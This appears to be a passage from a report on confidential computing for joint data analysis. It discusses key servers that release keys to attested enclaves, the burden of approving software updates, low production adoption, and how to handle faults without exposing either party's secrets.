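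**Key management** is another weak point. A party can upload encrypted material and leave the key with a key server, which releases the key only to an enclave whose report matches the approved software. Nvidia describes a design that bases this decision on evidence from both the CPU and the GPU. In a joint analysis, each side should control its own key server. Otherwise, one side could release the other's secrets.

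Both sides have to approve each new version of Google's Confidential Space software before their key servers will accept it, because each version changes the measurements. Google released seven versions between 20 January and 10 August 2026, or about one a month. The two sides may miss a security fix if they delay approval, but approving updates automatically removes much of the check's value.

These gaps are also why nobody has yet built the simple display that participants in the 2024 pilot wanted. A browser can show a padlock because websites use a common certificate format, browsers agree on whom to trust, and the check is automatic. Enclaves would need all three before a lawyer or a biologist could rely on a similar symbol.

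Gekker and colleagues describe the gap between demonstrations and production systems as "substantial". In a survey of more than 600 IT leaders, cited by Forough and colleagues, 18% of organisations had confidential computing in production, while 57% were still piloting or testing it. Joint analysis is probably further behind, because most of these organisations only need to protect their own data.

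Gekker and colleagues identify handling faults as one of the barriers. Engineers normally examine the machine's memory and logs to investigate a fault, but in an enclave those may contain both sides' secrets. The institute and the company should therefore agree before the test what the program may report if it fails, who may read those reports, and when to abandon the run instead of investigating it.
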